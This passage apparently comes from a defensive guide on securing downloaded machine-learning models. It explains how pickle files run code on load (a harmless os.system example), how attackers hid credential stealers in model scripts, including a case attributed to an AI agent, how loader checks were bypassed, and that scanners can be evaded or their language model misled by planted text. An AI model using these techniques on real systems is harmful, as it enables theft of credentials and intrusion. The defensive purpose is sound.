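The software then downloads only that version, even if the model is later updated. If someone else registers the account name and uploads their own files, the recorded commit will not exist in the new repository, so the download will fail rather than fetch those files. The setting also accepts labels such as `main`, but these give no such protection because they can move to a newer version. Saraf and Balassiano recommend fixing the revision and, for sensitive systems, scanning the model thoroughly and then keeping a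 copy in the company's own storage.

The price is that corrections no longer arrive automatically. Someone has to notice each new version, review it and change the identifier.

A hash lets a company check a file without relying on the hub to send the right one. SHA-256, the usual method, turns a file of any size into a number written as 64 characters. The hash of "hello" starts with `2cf24dba` and that of "Hello" with `185f8db3`, so capitalizing one letter produces an unrelated result. There are 2²⁵⁶ (about 10⁷⁷) possible hashes, and nobody knows a practical way to construct a different file with a given hash.

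To check a model file with a hash, engineers calculate the hash of the file they downloaded and compare it with the expected hash. The difficult part is getting the expected hash from a trustworthy source. If it is on the same page as the file, whoever replaced the file could have replaced the hash too. If the engineers calculated it from their own first download, a later match shows only that the file has not changed since then.

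A signature connects the hashes to a person or organisation. The signer keeps a private key secret and publishes a matching public key. Software uses the private key to calculate a signature from a piece of data, and anyone with the public key can check that the signature matches the data. Without the private key, nobody can produce a valid signature for altered data.

Models need a slightly more complex signing method because they consist of many files, some of them very large. The format from OpenSSF, a foundation for open-source software security, starts with a list of all the files and their hashes. The publisher signs the list and stores the result in a separate small file, which leaves the model unchanged. To check the model, the customer's software recalculates the hash of every file, compares the results with the list, and verifies the signature on the list. The check fails if someone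 has altered, removed or replaced any of the files.

The customer also has to know whose key it is. Red Hat's *Model authenticity and transparency with Sigstore* describes several options. A publisher can use a bare key, which carries no information about its owner, or a certificate, which ties a key to a name. Publishers can sign their own certificates, but many organisations' security policies discourage this because the only evidence for the name is the publisher's word. A certificate authority that the customer already trusts can issue the certificate instead.

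Sigstore, a free signing service, lets publishers sign models without guarding a key for years. The publisher logs in through an existing account, such as a work email. Sigstore issues a certificate that lasts a few minutes and links a temporary key to that account, and it records the signature in a public log. According to Sigstore's *Taming the Wild West of ML*, the customer then checks that the model was signed by the identity they expect and that the expected login provider vouched for it. The customer needs to know which identity to expect because the publisher of a look-alike model can sign it with their own email address, and the signature will be valid for that address.

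The following table compares the three checks for each way of getting the wrong model. The entries are based on how the checks work rather than on measured success rates, which would mean little for a comparison of hashes.

| What went wrong | Fixed revision | Hash from a reliable source | Signature by the expected signer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Engineer chose a look-alike | No help: it fixes the impostor's version | Detects it if the hash came from the real developer | Detects it |
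| Someone re-registered a deleted account name | Download fails | Detects it | Detects it |
| Someone hijacked the publisher's account | Protects versions recorded before the hijacking | Detects a change from an earlier, clean file | Detects it unless the intruder can also sign |
| Publisher released a harmful update | Keeps the older version | Detects that the file is different | No help if the publisher signed the update |
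| Someone altered files inside the hub | Depends on the hub's systems | Detects it if the hash predates the change or came from elsewhere | Detects it if the signing key was kept outside the hub |
| Model was harmful from the start | No help | No help | No help |

A valid signature identifies the signer and shows that the files have not changed since they were signed, but it does not show that the model is safe. An honest developer might sign a model without knowing that someone had tampered with its training data, and a criminal can sign malware. A signature still gives investigators a name to start with and lets a company refuse everything from a signer who has proved unreliable.

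OpenSSF argues that signing is especially important for models because the team that trains one is usually not the team that uses it. Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues (2025) announced the first full version of the signing tools only on 4 April 2025, in *Launch of Model Signing v1.0*, on behalf of a project led by people from Google, NVIDIA and HiddenLayer. NVIDIA has built signing into the publishing process for all the models it hosts in its own catalogue, NGC. According to HiddenLayer, Google's Kaggle is also adopting the format. NVIDIA's commitment is clear, but it covers only one company's catalogue and doesn't show what share of the three million models on Hugging Face are signed.

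NVIDIA's *Model Signature Verification* also shows that the check takes little work. A user downloads the signature and NVIDIA's certificate, then runs one command on the model's folder. Both the signature and the certificate come from NVIDIA's own services, so an intruder who controlled those services could replace them along with the model. A company that uses several of these models could guard against this by keeping the certificate from its first download and investigating if a later one differs.

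### Tracing the parts of the claims assistant

The insurer got its language model from account A, which had compressed the developer's release. Compression changes the file, so its hash cannot match the developer's, even if account A acted honestly. The engineers could compress the original themselves and compare the results, but the files would match only if the engineers knew the exact tool and settings and the process gave the same result every time.

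Doing without account A is simpler. Suppose the developer signs its release through Sigstore and gives the signing address on its website. The engineers follow the website's link to the hub, note the full commit identifier and download that version with its signature. They check the signature using the address from the website and the login provider they expect. If the check succeeds and the scans in the next step find nothing, they compress the model, record the settings and the new hash, and sign the compressed version with the insurer's own key. The server that runs the assistant can then refuse any model without the insurer's signature. This also helps protect against people who can alter models in the company's own storage, a concern raised by the Coalition for Secure AI, as long as those people cannot use the signing key.

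The chat template is easier to check because it is short. The engineers can compare account A's copy with the developer's line by line. If the two are identical, they can rule out a change by account A. If they differ, somebody has to read and explain every difference, or the insurer can use the developer's version, which it now has.

If the engineers downloaded the retrieval model from the developer's own account, but the developer does not sign its models, they can confirm the account from the developer's website, pin the revision and keep the hash. These steps protect the insurer from later changes, but they do not independently show that the first download was genuine. For that, the insurer depends on the hub and on the security of the developer's account.

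The engineers cannot trace the adapter beyond account B. No developer's website links to that account, and there is no original to compare the adapter with. Even if account B signed the adapter, the certificate would show an email address that nobody at the insurer recognises. The engineers can still fix the adapter's revision and record its hash to make sure they use the same file they tested. They also need to check how the adapter loads its base model. The software can fetch the base model by a name written in the adapter's settings, and if that name has no fixed revision, the assistant could run on a different language model from the one the engineers verified.

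## Scanning model files for hidden code

The insurer has traced its language model and retrieval model to their developers and pinned the adapter from account B to one revision. Nobody should open these files yet, because some formats let a file run code when opened. Suppose the two traced models are safetensors files and the adapter is a `.bin` file made with PyTorch, the main software for developing models. The adapter needs the closest look because PyTorch normally saves files in pickle, which is one of the formats that can run code.

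### How opening a pickle file runs code

A pickle file contains instructions for rebuilding a Python object, and Python carries them out in order when someone opens the file. Most of the instructions do routine work, such as creating a number or adding it to a list. Others look up a Python function by name and call it with inputs from the file. Legitimate models need these too, for example to call the function that arranges stored numbers into a table of weights. But as Kellas, Li and colleagues (2025) explain in *PICKLEBALL*, a pickle file can call almost any Python function. One of them is `os.system`, which passes a command to the operating system. In simplified form, a file that uses it looks like this:

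```
GLOBAL   os.system       look up the function
STRING   "echo hello"    supply its input
TUPLE                    package the input
REDUCE                   call the function
STOP                     finish
```

This example only prints "hello". An attacker would choose a different command. It would run before the model was used, with the permissions of the program that opened the file.

Python can generate these instructions automatically. When it saves an object, it can call a method named `__reduce__`, which returns a function and its inputs. Python writes both into the file and calls the function when someone loads the file. If `__reduce__` returns a harmful function, saving the object in the usual way produces a harmful file.

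*I Don't Care How You Hide It, I Care What You Do* (Ali and Case, 2026) describes a case from March 2026. Someone uploaded a repository to Hugging Face that looked like a Qwen2 language model, which should have had about 300 megabytes of weights, but the model file was only 10.2 kilobytes. Opening it started a connection that let an attacker run commands on the user's computer. The repository had 108 downloads in three days, and none of the hub's scanners had flagged it. Comparing the file's size with that of a real Qwen2 model would have shown that something was wrong.

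### What other formats allow

*On the (In)Security of Loading Machine Learning Models* (Digregorio, Di Gennaro et al., 2025) calls pickle a code-based format because it stores instructions for rebuilding a model. Data-based formats store a description of the model instead. They are generally safer, but several still allow code.

| Format | What a file contains | How it could run code |
|---|---|---|
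| Pickle, including most PyTorch `.pt`, `.pth` and `.bin` files | Instructions for rebuilding Python objects | Calls functions when someone opens the file, or creates an object that does so when someone uses the model |
| Safetensors | A short description and the weights | Contains no instructions to run |
| GGUF | Weights, settings and a chat template | Not through the weights, but the template is a script that runs with each prompt |
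| ONNX | Weights and a plan of calculations, built from a fixed set of operations | Cannot hold Python code, but attackers could misuse some operations in particular settings |
| Keras, current `.keras` format | Weights and a description of the model | Python code in a "Lambda layer", which a safe mode blocks by default |
| Keras, older `.h5` format | Weights and a description of the model | Python code in a Lambda layer, with no safe mode |
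| TensorFlow SavedModel | Weights and a plan of calculations | Operations that read files or use the network |

Safetensors is the simplest of these formats. According to Hugging Face's *Safetensors is Joining the PyTorch Foundation* (2026), a file starts with a header of at most 100 megabytes that describes the tables of weights, and the rest is numbers. It is now the default format on the hub. The security company Trail of Bits audited the software that reads these files, and EleutherAI's *Audit shows that safetensors is safe and ready to become the default* reports that the results allowed wider use of the format. The format is safe partly because it does not store the program that does the model's calculations, so the user needs to get that program elsewhere. For an unusual model, it may be a script in the same repository, which a scan of the weights doesn't cover.

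GGUF files also store their weights as plain data. Their weak point is the chat template. *GGUF LLM Models with Hidden Malware on Hugging Face Reached 2400+ Victims* (Düzgün, 2026) describes a November 2026 campaign in which attackers altered this template.

A TensorFlow SavedModel file can use only TensorFlow's own operations, but some of those can read files or contact other computers, and researchers have combined them into attacks that give access to a command line. Nabeel and Starov, in *Deep Dive into the Abuse of DL APIs* (2026), consider the format inherently more secure than pickle because it doesn't support running arbitrary Python code directly. Digregorio and colleagues list arbitrary code execution as possible by design, which is compatible with that view. When Kellas and colleagues wrote in 2025, nobody had observed a real attack through SavedModel or ONNX, so the evidence for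 both is at the level "demonstrated".

A format's safety also depends on the software that opens it. Digregorio and colleagues tested loading methods that developers advertise as secure and found six previously unknown flaws, including some in Keras's safe mode, each of which let a file run arbitrary code. They also surveyed practitioners and found that names like "safe mode" made people trust these settings more than the test results justified.

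### How common pickle still is

Kellas and colleagues studied Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month. In March 2025 there were 16,661 of them, and 44.9% contained pickle files. Of the 100 most downloaded models, 29 were available only as pickle.

*DITTO* (Qin, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports a much lower figure for newer models. Of 10,023 repositories created between July 2025 and June 2026 with more than 1,000 downloads a month, 929 (9.3%) contained pickle files. The difference from the earlier 44.9% doesn't measure a decline over time, because Kellas and colleagues included popular repositories of any age and judged each file's format by its extension, while Qin and colleagues counted only recent repositories and opened or inspected doubtful files. Still, the figures suggest that most new models come in safer formats while many older pickle files remain in use.

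Pickle files also turn up beside safer ones, because some people who fine-tune a safetensors model publish the result with a pickle file that records their training settings. A company with a "safetensors only" rule therefore needs to check every file in the repository. GGUF is also common. *Five Malicious AI Models on Hugging Face Hid a Windows Trojan* (Faisal, 2026) counts 226,310 GGUF repositories in late November 2026, about 7% of all public model repositories on the hub.

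Hugging Face scans pickle files automatically and displays the results, but these do not always give reviewers a clear answer. Of the 9,544 pickle files that Qin and colleagues identified, 5,840 were labeled "safe", 2,998 "caution" and 21 "unsafe". The other 685 had no valid result.

### Lists of forbidden and permitted functions

Most scanners read a pickle file's instructions without running them and check the functions the file names against a list. ModelScan uses a list of forbidden functions, so it recognises common attacks quickly but misses any harmful function its developers did not include. Fickling uses a list of permitted functions and flags the rest. This is stricter, but machine-learning software uses so many functions that a short list produces constant alarms. PickleScan, which Hugging Face uses on its hub, combines both kinds of list.

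Neither kind of list handles functions with both harmless and harmful uses well. JFrog (2025) gives an example from YOLO, a family of models that find objects in pictures. A YOLO file calls `getattr`, which fetches part of a Python object by name, to get the model's own `forward` function. The model needs this to work, but `getattr` could also fetch a function that runs system commands. A scanner that forbids `getattr` will flag harmless YOLO models, and one that permits it may miss an attack.

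DITTO, the scanner that Qin and colleagues developed, examines how a file uses each function. It follows and records the file's instructions step by step, replacing sensitive ones with placeholders so that it never calls a suspicious function. It then removes routine steps from the record and passes the rest to a language model, which classifies the remaining steps as part of normal loading or not. With `getattr`, for instance, the language model can check whether the file fetched `forward` or something that runs commands.

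### Restricted loaders

When a scanner reports a suspicious function, someone then has to decide whether to open the file. A restricted loader opens the file but refuses to use any function outside a permitted list. PyTorch has had one since version 1.13, through the `weights_only` setting, and has used it by default since version 2.6. The standard list covers a small set of functions that PyTorch needs to rebuild weights.

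Kellas and colleagues tested how often models use functions that PyTorch's restricted loader refuses. They were able to analyse 1,426 of the 1,500 most popular repositories whose models were available only as pickle. In 219 of them, or 15.4%, at least one model used such a function. Those repositories had 79.6 million downloads in one month. The developers of flair, a text-analysis library, switch the restricted loader off because their models would not open otherwise. Flair's users have to depend on a scanner's warning and their own judgement.

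PickleBall, the method Kellas and colleagues propose, makes separate lists of permitted functions for each library. It starts with the type of model the user expects and analyzes the library's source code to work out which functions that type needs. One list contains the functions that the file may look up, and a shorter list contains those it may call. If the file looks up anything else, PickleBall substitutes a placeholder that raises an error only if the program tries to use it. A model can then still open if, for example, the replaced function belongs to an old training record that nobody needs.

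In tests on 252 harmless models from 16 libraries and 84 malicious ones, PickleBall stopped every malicious model and correctly loaded 201 of the harmless ones (79.8%). PyTorch's restricted loader also stopped all 84 malicious models but loaded only 157 harmless ones (62.3%). The 95 harmless models it refused all came from flair, PyAnnote and two versions of YOLO, and it loaded every harmless model from the other 12 libraries. It refused 38% of the harmless models here but had trouble with only 15.4% of repositories in the broader sample because the test set contained many models from those four libraries.

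PickleBall also had trouble with YOLO models, which made up 44 of the 51 harmless models it blocked. These YOLO files used different names from the library for the same functions. Kellas and colleagues had to edit the source code of five of the 16 libraries by hand before PickleBall could analyse them. A restricted loader also cannot rule out an attack that combines only permitted functions to cause harm, although the researchers knew of no such attack.

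Restricted loaders can have flaws of their own. MITRE's *CVE-2026-24747* (2026) describes one in PyTorch versions before 2.10.0. A specially made file could corrupt memory and potentially run code even with `weights_only` switched on. The record listed no known exploitation in January 2026. Version 2.10.0 fixed the flaw, so engineers who rely on this setting should check their PyTorch version.

### Watching a model run

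A reviewer can open a model file in an isolated environment and watch what it does, rather than try to predict it. Ali and Case's ModelShield loads the model, gives it a made-up input, and records every request to the operating system, such as a request to open a file or connect to another computer.

Loading a harmless model can produce thousands of these requests. ModelShield therefore links each request to the step that caused it and compares the sequence with 195 patterns of harmful behaviour. One pattern consists of reading a file that holds login keys, connecting to an outside address and sending data there. Reading the keys doesn't trigger an alert on its own, because harmless software sometimes opens sensitive files.

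Tests for hidden code should run the model as well as load it. ModelShield found 41 malicious models on Hugging Face in spring 2026, and 19 of them ran their code only when someone used the model. A monitor that covered only the loading step would have missed those 19. But no monitor can detect behavior triggered by conditions that don't arise in the test, such as a certain date, a particular input, or running on Windows when the test machine uses Linux.

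Monitoring also takes longer. ModelShield needed a median of 12.3 seconds per model, compared with 0.07 seconds for PickleScan and 2.3 seconds for ModelScan. The extra time matters to a hub that receives thousands of models a day but makes little difference to an insurer with three models.

### How the tools compare on the same files

Ali and Case ran several tools on the PickleBall test set of 84 malicious and 252 harmless files. The figures for PyTorch's restricted loader in the following table come from Kellas and colleagues, who used the same files. For the loaders, "wrongly flagged" means they refused to load a harmless model.

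| Tool | Method | Malicious files caught, of 84 | Harmless files wrongly flagged, of 252 |
|---|---|---|---|
| PickleScan | Forbidden and permitted lists | 79 | 16 |
| ModelScan | Forbidden list | 75 | 16 |
| ModelAudit | Forbidden list and known flaws | 82 | 91 |
| Fickling | Permitted list | 2 | 252 |
| PyTorch's restricted loader | Permitted list, applied while loading | 84 | 95 |
| PickleBall | Separate permitted list for each library | 84 | 51 |
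| DynaHug | Monitoring during loading | 84 | 252 |
| ModelShield | Monitoring during loading and use | 47 | 0 |

DynaHug caught every malicious file, but only because it marked every file as malicious. Its developers had trained it on text-generating models, and it flagged other kinds as suspicious. Fickling did badly because it could not read the archives in which PyTorch packs its pickle files, so its result reflects that fault more than how well permitted lists work in general.

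ModelShield missed 37 files, but Ali and Case examined each one and found that 28 could not have done harm. In 23 of these, the code ran but did nothing harmful, and in 16 of those 23 it only printed a message. Four others contained broken code or needed a file that wasn't there, and one was a harmless model with the wrong label. Of the 56 files that could have done harm, ModelShield caught 47. It caught five more once the necessary packages were installed, and the remaining four worked only on Windows.

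Whether to count the other misses depends on what the reviewer wants to know. A file that prints "hello" is harmless, but someone has still put code in it that doesn't belong in a model. PickleScan is useful for finding such files, and ModelShield is useful for finding harmful ones. Ali and Case recommend using both kinds of tool.

The test set is also biased, because Kellas and colleagues took 82 of the 84 malicious files from collections that earlier scanners had found and made the other two themselves. It therefore contains few files that those scanners missed, and the detection rates may be too high. In a separate test of 29 published ways to evade detection, ModelShield caught all of them and none of the file scanners did.

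### Why false-alarm rates differ

PickleScan wrongly flagged 16 of the 252 harmless files in the PickleBall set (6.3%) and 177 of the 697 in Qin and colleagues' study (25.4%).

Much of the difference probably comes from the choice of files. The PickleBall set contains popular models from 16 selected libraries. Qin and colleagues started with 685 files for which Hugging Face had no valid scan result, and added 21 that Hugging Face had labelled "unsafe" but they found harmless. PickleScan could read 697 of these 706 files. As expected, it flagged all 21 "unsafe" files again, since Hugging Face itself uses PickleScan. Without those 21 files, its false-alarm rate would still have been about 23%.

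The choice of files doesn't seem to fully explain the difference. Qin and colleagues later combined their files with the PickleBall set into a benchmark of 959 harmless and 92 malicious files. PickleScan wrongly flagged 28.7% of the harmless files it could read, or about 270. Subtracting the earlier 177 leaves more than 90 false alarms among the PickleBall files, where Ali and Case had counted 16. The two teams may have used different versions of PickleScan, or one may have counted warnings about unfamiliar functions that the other ignored. A company that relies on a published error rate should check what the researchers counted as an alert.

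On the combined benchmark, DITTO caught all 92 malicious files and wrongly flagged an average of seven harmless ones, or 0.7%. These results come from the tool's developers and depend on the language model inside it. When the developers replaced the default, a DeepSeek model, with GPT-4.1-nano, DITTO missed 24 malicious files, mostly simple demonstrations. With Gemini-3.1-flash-lite, it made no mistakes. A malicious file could also contain text meant to mislead the language model. DITTO still worked correctly on the one example of this that Qin and colleagues report, though they accept that a more sophisticated attempt might succeed.

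### What an alert means when malicious models are rare

PickleScan raised 95 alerts on the PickleBall dataset, where one file in four is malicious, and 79 of those alerts (83%) were correct. On a hub where almost every file is harmless, nearly all of its alerts would be false.

Suppose a hub has a million pickle files, 100 of them malicious. At its test rates, PickleScan would catch 94.0% of the malicious files, or 94, and wrongly flag 6.3% of the 999,900 harmless ones, or about 63,000. Only about 0.15% of its alerts would be correct, because the hub has far more harmless files for each malicious one than the test did.

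If *p* is the share of files that are malicious, *d* the detection rate and *f* the false-alarm rate, the share of alerts that are correct is

*p* × *d* / (*p* × *d* + (1 − *p*) × *f*).

The answer depends heavily on *p*, which nobody knows exactly. The last column of the next table shows the chance that a file is malicious even though PickleScan did not flag it.

| Assumed share of malicious files | Alerts that are correct | Chance that an unflagged file is malicious |
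|---|---|---|
| 1 in 4, as in the test set | 83% | 1 in 48 |
| 1 in 100 | 13% | 1 in 1,560 |
| 1 in 1,000 | 1.5% | 1 in 15,700 |
| 1 in 10,000 | 0.15% | 1 in 157,000 |
| 1 in 100,000 | 0.015% | 1 in 1.57 million |

Large scans give some idea of which row is realistic. Ali and Case cite an earlier study that found 91 malicious models among more than 705,000 on Hugging Face, about 1 in 7,700. Their own scan found 41 among 105,000 recent uploads, or 1 in 2,600, and another 105 among 224,164 when they continued it until August 2026. They describe only four of these 146 models as real-world malware, which is about 1 in 82,000 of the models scanned. The share depends on whether harmless demonstrations count as malicious. These figures cover models in every format, and the share would be higher among pickle files alone. ModelShield also misses some malicious models, so the true numbers are larger.

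Ali and Case also ran the file scanners on 10,000 models from Hugging Face and checked the alerts by hand. At least one scanner flagged 565 of the models, but only eight of those (1.4%) were malicious. The formula gives 1.2% if eight in 10,000 files are malicious and PickleScan performs as it did on the test set. The close match is partly luck, since several scanners contributed to the 565 flags, but it supports the conclusion that most alerts on a public hub are false.

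JFrog made a similar claim in March 2025, when it announced that its own scanner would check models on Hugging Face. It said that more than 96% of the models that pickle scanning had marked "unsafe" were false alarms, based on its own analysis of all the models with that label. JFrog says these findings led it to develop the scanner, which extracts the code from a file, converts it into a readable form, and examines how the file uses suspicious functions. The exact number deserves caution because JFrog sells the scanner and does not explain in the announcement how it checked the models. JFrog also promises in the announcement to eliminate 96% of existing false alarms, which is a different claim. Still, Ali and Case found an even higher share of false alarms in their hand check, and all 21 of the "unsafe" files that Qin and colleagues inspected were harmless. Hugging Face also notes on its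 *Third-party scanner* page that code inside a model file is not always malicious.

JFrog's 96% is the share of alerts that are wrong, while PickleScan's false-alarm rate of 6.3% is the share of harmless files that set off an alert, so the two figures don't contradict each other.

An alert is still worth investigating. If one file in 10,000 is malicious, an alert raises the chance that the flagged file is malicious to about 1 in 670. A company also scans far fewer files than a hub does. If the insurer scanned 50 harmless pickle files a year, it could expect about three false alarms, and its security staff would have time to investigate them.

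### What a clean scan adds

If PickleScan finds nothing in a file, the file is about 16 times less likely to be malicious than it was before the scan. For the insurer's adapter, the estimated risk before scanning matters more than usual because nobody knows who runs account B. The reviewers would have to guess this risk, as no study has measured the rate of malicious adapters from unidentified publishers. If they guessed 1 in 100, an alert would raise the chance that the adapter is malicious to 13%, and a clean scan would lower it to about 1 in 1,560.

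The second figure is probably too reassuring, because it assumes that PickleScan catches 94% of malicious files. Of the 41 malicious models that ModelShield found on Hugging Face, PickleScan caught only 23, or 56%. At that rate, a clean scan would lower the chance that a file is malicious from 1 in 100 to only about 1 in 210. An attacker can also run a public scanner on a file before uploading it, and change the file until the scanner finds nothing.

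One of those 41 models resembled the insurer's adapter. Its repository contained two `.bin` files with names typical of adapter weights. When Ali and Case loaded the model, it collected details about the computer and its user accounts and sent them to outside servers. A harmless adapter can also set off an alert. All three scanners that Qin and colleagues compared flagged one because it used `getattr` to look up ordinary training settings. The scanner's label doesn't distinguish these two cases, so the reviewers need to see which functions the scanner found and what the file does with them.

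Scanning the adapter with a second tool would help most if that tool worked differently from the first. Two scanners with similar lists are likely to miss the same files, so a second clean result adds little. PickleScan and ModelShield fail for different reasons, so clean results from both are more informative. Neither tool can detect a backdoor in the adapter's weights.

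## Choosing safe loading settings and tracing flagged models

The reviewers have scanned the insurer's model files, and the engineers can now load them. Some authors publish Python scripts with their models, and the engineers' settings determine whether these scripts run and what they can access.

### Why some models need their authors' code

Transformers, Hugging Face's library for running models, already includes the code for most language models. A settings file in the repository names the model's design, and the library uses its own code for that design. If researchers have invented something new, such as a different way to represent word order, the library has no code for it yet, so they publish their own. Siddiq, Romel and colleagues (2026) explain in *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* that users would otherwise have to rebuild the design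 themselves.

Transformers runs these scripts only if the engineer adds `trust_remote_code=True` to the loading command. The scripts can then do anything the engineer's own program can do, such as read files, open network connections or start other programs. The setting doesn't make the library check them for harmful code.

Siddiq and colleagues found custom code in 36,697 of 2,107,935 Hugging Face repositories (1.74%). They counted every repository with certain tags or file names, so some of these models may also load without their scripts. Most of the models (64.4%) generate text, and another 13% do feature extraction, as the insurer's retrieval model does. Custom code was more common on two other large hubs, OpenCSG (3.20%) and ModelScope (4.65%).

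The researchers also read 612 developer discussions about this setting and its PyTorch equivalent. Some developers thought it only allowed the library to read a model's description, and others confused it with fixing a revision. The discussions don't show how common these mistakes are. Still, a reviewer who finds `trust_remote_code=True` in a colleague's program shouldn't assume that the colleague meant to let outside code run.

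### Weaknesses in the scripts

Siddiq and colleagues checked the scripts for weaknesses, meaning mistakes that an attacker might be able to exploit. They first narrowed 128,487 Python files from five hubs to the 67,009 that could run when a model loads. They then scanned these with Bandit, Semgrep and CodeQL, which look for risky programming practices, and YARA, which looks for patterns that identify malware and other kinds of file.

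| Tool | Hugging Face repositories with a finding, of 36,697 | Most common finding |
|---|---|---|
| Bandit | 2,824 (7.70%) | `assert` statements (78.16% of findings) |
| Semgrep | 1,691 (4.60%) | Use of the NumPy library in PyTorch code (42.29%), followed by use of pickle (33.83%) |
| CodeQL | 1,894 (5.16%) | Comparisons that might reveal a secret through their timing (98.48%) |
| YARA | 2,562 (6.98%) | The pattern of a file format for 3D drawings (82.54%) |

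Bandit's 7.70% is less alarming than it sounds. An `assert` statement stops a program if a condition is false. Python has a mode that skips these statements, but this is a security risk only if the program relies on one for protection. Bandit therefore rates them as low severity. The most common high-severity problem accounted for 56 findings, or 0.06%.

Some of the other findings may be false alarms caused by the two meanings of "token". In security software it is usually a login credential, but in language-model code it is a piece of text, often shorter than a word. A tool that looks for secrets partly by variable name can mistake the text for a credential. This might explain CodeQL's many warnings about secrets and some of the 10,097 hard-coded passwords that Bandit reported. Siddiq and colleagues cite an earlier study in which about 91% of Bandit's findings were correct, but they don't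 report checking these warnings by hand.

The 7.70% doesn't measure how many repositories are malicious, because even a genuine weakness can appear in code written without malicious intent. Semgrep found 494 uses of `eval`, a Python function that runs text as code. An honest researcher might use it to read a number from a settings file, which becomes dangerous if an attacker can change that file. A script written to steal passwords could also contain no weakness that these tools detect.

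YARA comes closer to looking for attacks, but its results are hard to interpret. Apart from the 3D format, its most common matches were signs of virtual machine software. Malware often checks for a virtual machine so it can stay inactive while researchers examine it, but ordinary programs may refer to the same software. Siddiq and colleagues call such matches malicious code in their conclusion, but in their results they describe them as indicators without clear evidence of malware, which fits the data better.

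The researchers also ran PickleScan, ModelScan and two other scanners on the repositories. The scanners found nothing in the scripts that run when a model loads, mainly because these tools are designed to inspect saved model files. The insurer's clean scans therefore provide little information about any scripts published with its models.

### Models that steal credentials

In November 2026, someone published scripts of this kind to steal credentials. ThreatRoundup's *An AI Agent Built Hugging Face Malware, Then Leaked Its Own Keys* (2026) summarises JFrog's report on the case, *The Agent That Robbed Itself*. On 24 November, a new Hugging Face account published a supposed language model named `llama-3.2-1b-tuned`, whose files contained a credential-stealing program instead of weights. JFrog concluded with high confidence that an AI agent had built, uploaded and tested it. The agent, ARTEX,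 carries out cyberattacks using a language model, in this case GPT-5.4. JFrog could not identify the person directing it.

The attackers had put the harmful code in the model's scripts and in two pickle files, and had also tampered with the chat template. Default settings in current software stopped two of these three routes. PyTorch 2.6 and later refuse to load such pickle files, and Transformers runs chat templates in a restricted environment, though some other programs for running models do not. The harmful scripts still ran for anyone who had set `trust_remote_code=True`, before the library read any weights.

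Once running, the code collected the program's environment variables, settings that often include passwords and access keys. It also looked for a credential for Kubernetes, a system for managing containers. It then uploaded what it found to the attackers' repository on Hugging Face. The first upload came from the agent's own test, 14 seconds after publication, and exposed the agent's access key and database password.

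Five hours later the account published a second model with scripts but no weights. Pickle scanners had nothing to inspect, and Hugging Face displayed no warning. An engineer could have noticed from the file list that the weights were missing. Hugging Face disabled all 13 of the account's repositories that day, and JFrog knew of no real victims, so the evidence level is "found in circulation".

### Code that ran without permission

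Leaving `trust_remote_code` off protects the user only if the library enforces the setting. Until May 2026, Diffusers, Hugging Face's library for models that generate images, video and audio, did not always enforce it. *FaceHugger* (Zaban and Shani, 2026), from the security company Zafran, describes flaws that let a repository run code on a user's computer without permission. This could happen even if the user had explicitly set the option to `False`, according to *GHSA-98h9-4798-4q5v* (OSV, 2026), an entry in a public database of software flaws.

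The flaws all arose because Diffusers checked for custom code at one stage of loading and ran it at another, so code that appeared only at the later stage escaped the check. The Hacker News lists three official records of the flaws, with severity scores of 7.5, 8.8 and 8.8 out of 10. One covers a mistake in how the two stages handled a missing setting, and another covers a change to the repository between two download requests. The third covers several variants, including one that affected files already on the user's computer.

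Infosecurity Magazine's *Bugs in Hugging Face Diffusers Bypass Custom Code Safeguard* reports that the change between requests had to happen within about 0.3 seconds in Zafran's tests. But an attacker could briefly publish a harmful change to a popular model, reverse it, and expect to catch some users by chance. GitLab's *Advisories for Pypi/Diffusers package* adds that loading finished normally and the model worked, so users would have had no obvious reason to be suspicious.

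Zafran reported the first two flaws on 19 March. Hugging Face fixed all three in version 0.38.0 on 1 May by moving the check to the stage that loads the code, and Zafran published its analysis on 27 July. None of these accounts describes an attack on a real user, so the risk is rated "demonstrated". People were installing Diffusers about 200,000 times a day, so many computers may have been exposed. A container built before May keeps the old version until someone rebuilds it.

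The claims assistant doesn't generate images, but it does use Transformers. Zafran disclosed a similar flaw in that library, and Hugging Face's security team had acknowledged it by July, according to Infosecurity Magazine. The engineers should therefore follow security updates for Transformers too, and not rely on the permission setting alone.

Fixing the revision should prevent an attack that depends on a change between requests, because both requests would return the same version.

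### Settings for the claims assistant

Suppose Transformers and its companion adapter library already support the designs of the insurer's language model and adapter, but the retrieval model needs its developer's scripts. Each part then needs different settings.

| Part | `trust_remote_code` | Other precautions |
|---|---|---|
| Language model (safetensors) | Off | Fix the revision |
| Adapter (pickle) | Off | Open it once in isolation with `weights_only=True`, then save the weights as safetensors |
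| Retrieval model (safetensors and scripts) | On, after someone has read the scripts | Fix the revision of the weights and the scripts; run the model in a separate process |

If the language model fails to load with permission to run outside code turned off, the engineers should find out why before changing the setting. The repository they downloaded may contain unnecessary scripts, or their version of Transformers may be too old for the model. Updating the library is safer than turning that permission on.

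For the adapter, the engineers can use PyTorch's restricted loader, in version 2.10.0 or later because of the flaw described earlier. If the file loads, they save the weights in safetensors format and stop using the original pickle file, so the production server never opens it. The conversion does not remove any backdoor in the weights.

The retrieval model takes more work because a programmer has to read every script that can run at loading, looking for network connections, access to environment variables, commands that start other programs, and text that the script turns into code. The programmer also has to check for further downloads, because a fixed revision doesn't cover files that a script fetches from elsewhere. Bandit found 3,803 unsafe downloads from Hugging Face in the scripts that Siddiq and colleagues examined. The model's settings can also refer to scripts in another repository,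 for which Transformers has a separate `code_revision` setting.

If nobody at the insurer can review the scripts, the simplest solution is to use a retrieval model that Transformers already supports. Some developers copy a model's scripts into their own program and edit them to run without the permission. This keeps out unexpected updates, but Siddiq and colleagues warn that it creates maintenance work and leaves doubts about security.

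Even with careful settings, the engineers should load each model for the first time in isolation. They download the fixed revision on one machine and copy it to another that has no network connection, passwords, access keys or customer documents. If harmful code runs there, it can steal little and can't send anything out. A virtual machine is a stronger barrier than a container, because containers share the core of the host's operating system. The engineers can delete the virtual machine after the test.

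Some models need a network connection during loading. ThreatRoundup recommends letting the machines that load them download from Hugging Face but blocking uploads. Limiting a machine to Hugging Face's website isn't enough, since the November attackers sent their stolen data there. In *js-logger-pack Operator Turns Hugging Face into a Malware CDN and Exfiltration Backend*, Satou (2026) describes another criminal operation that stored stolen data in private Hugging Face datasets.

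In Hugging Face's July 2026 breach, a malicious dataset exploited both a loader that ran outside code and a template in the dataset's settings, according to SC Media's *Hugging Face uses GLM 5.2 to investigate AI agent-driven cyberattack*. Keeping credentials away from machines that open outside files makes it harder for an intruder to get further.

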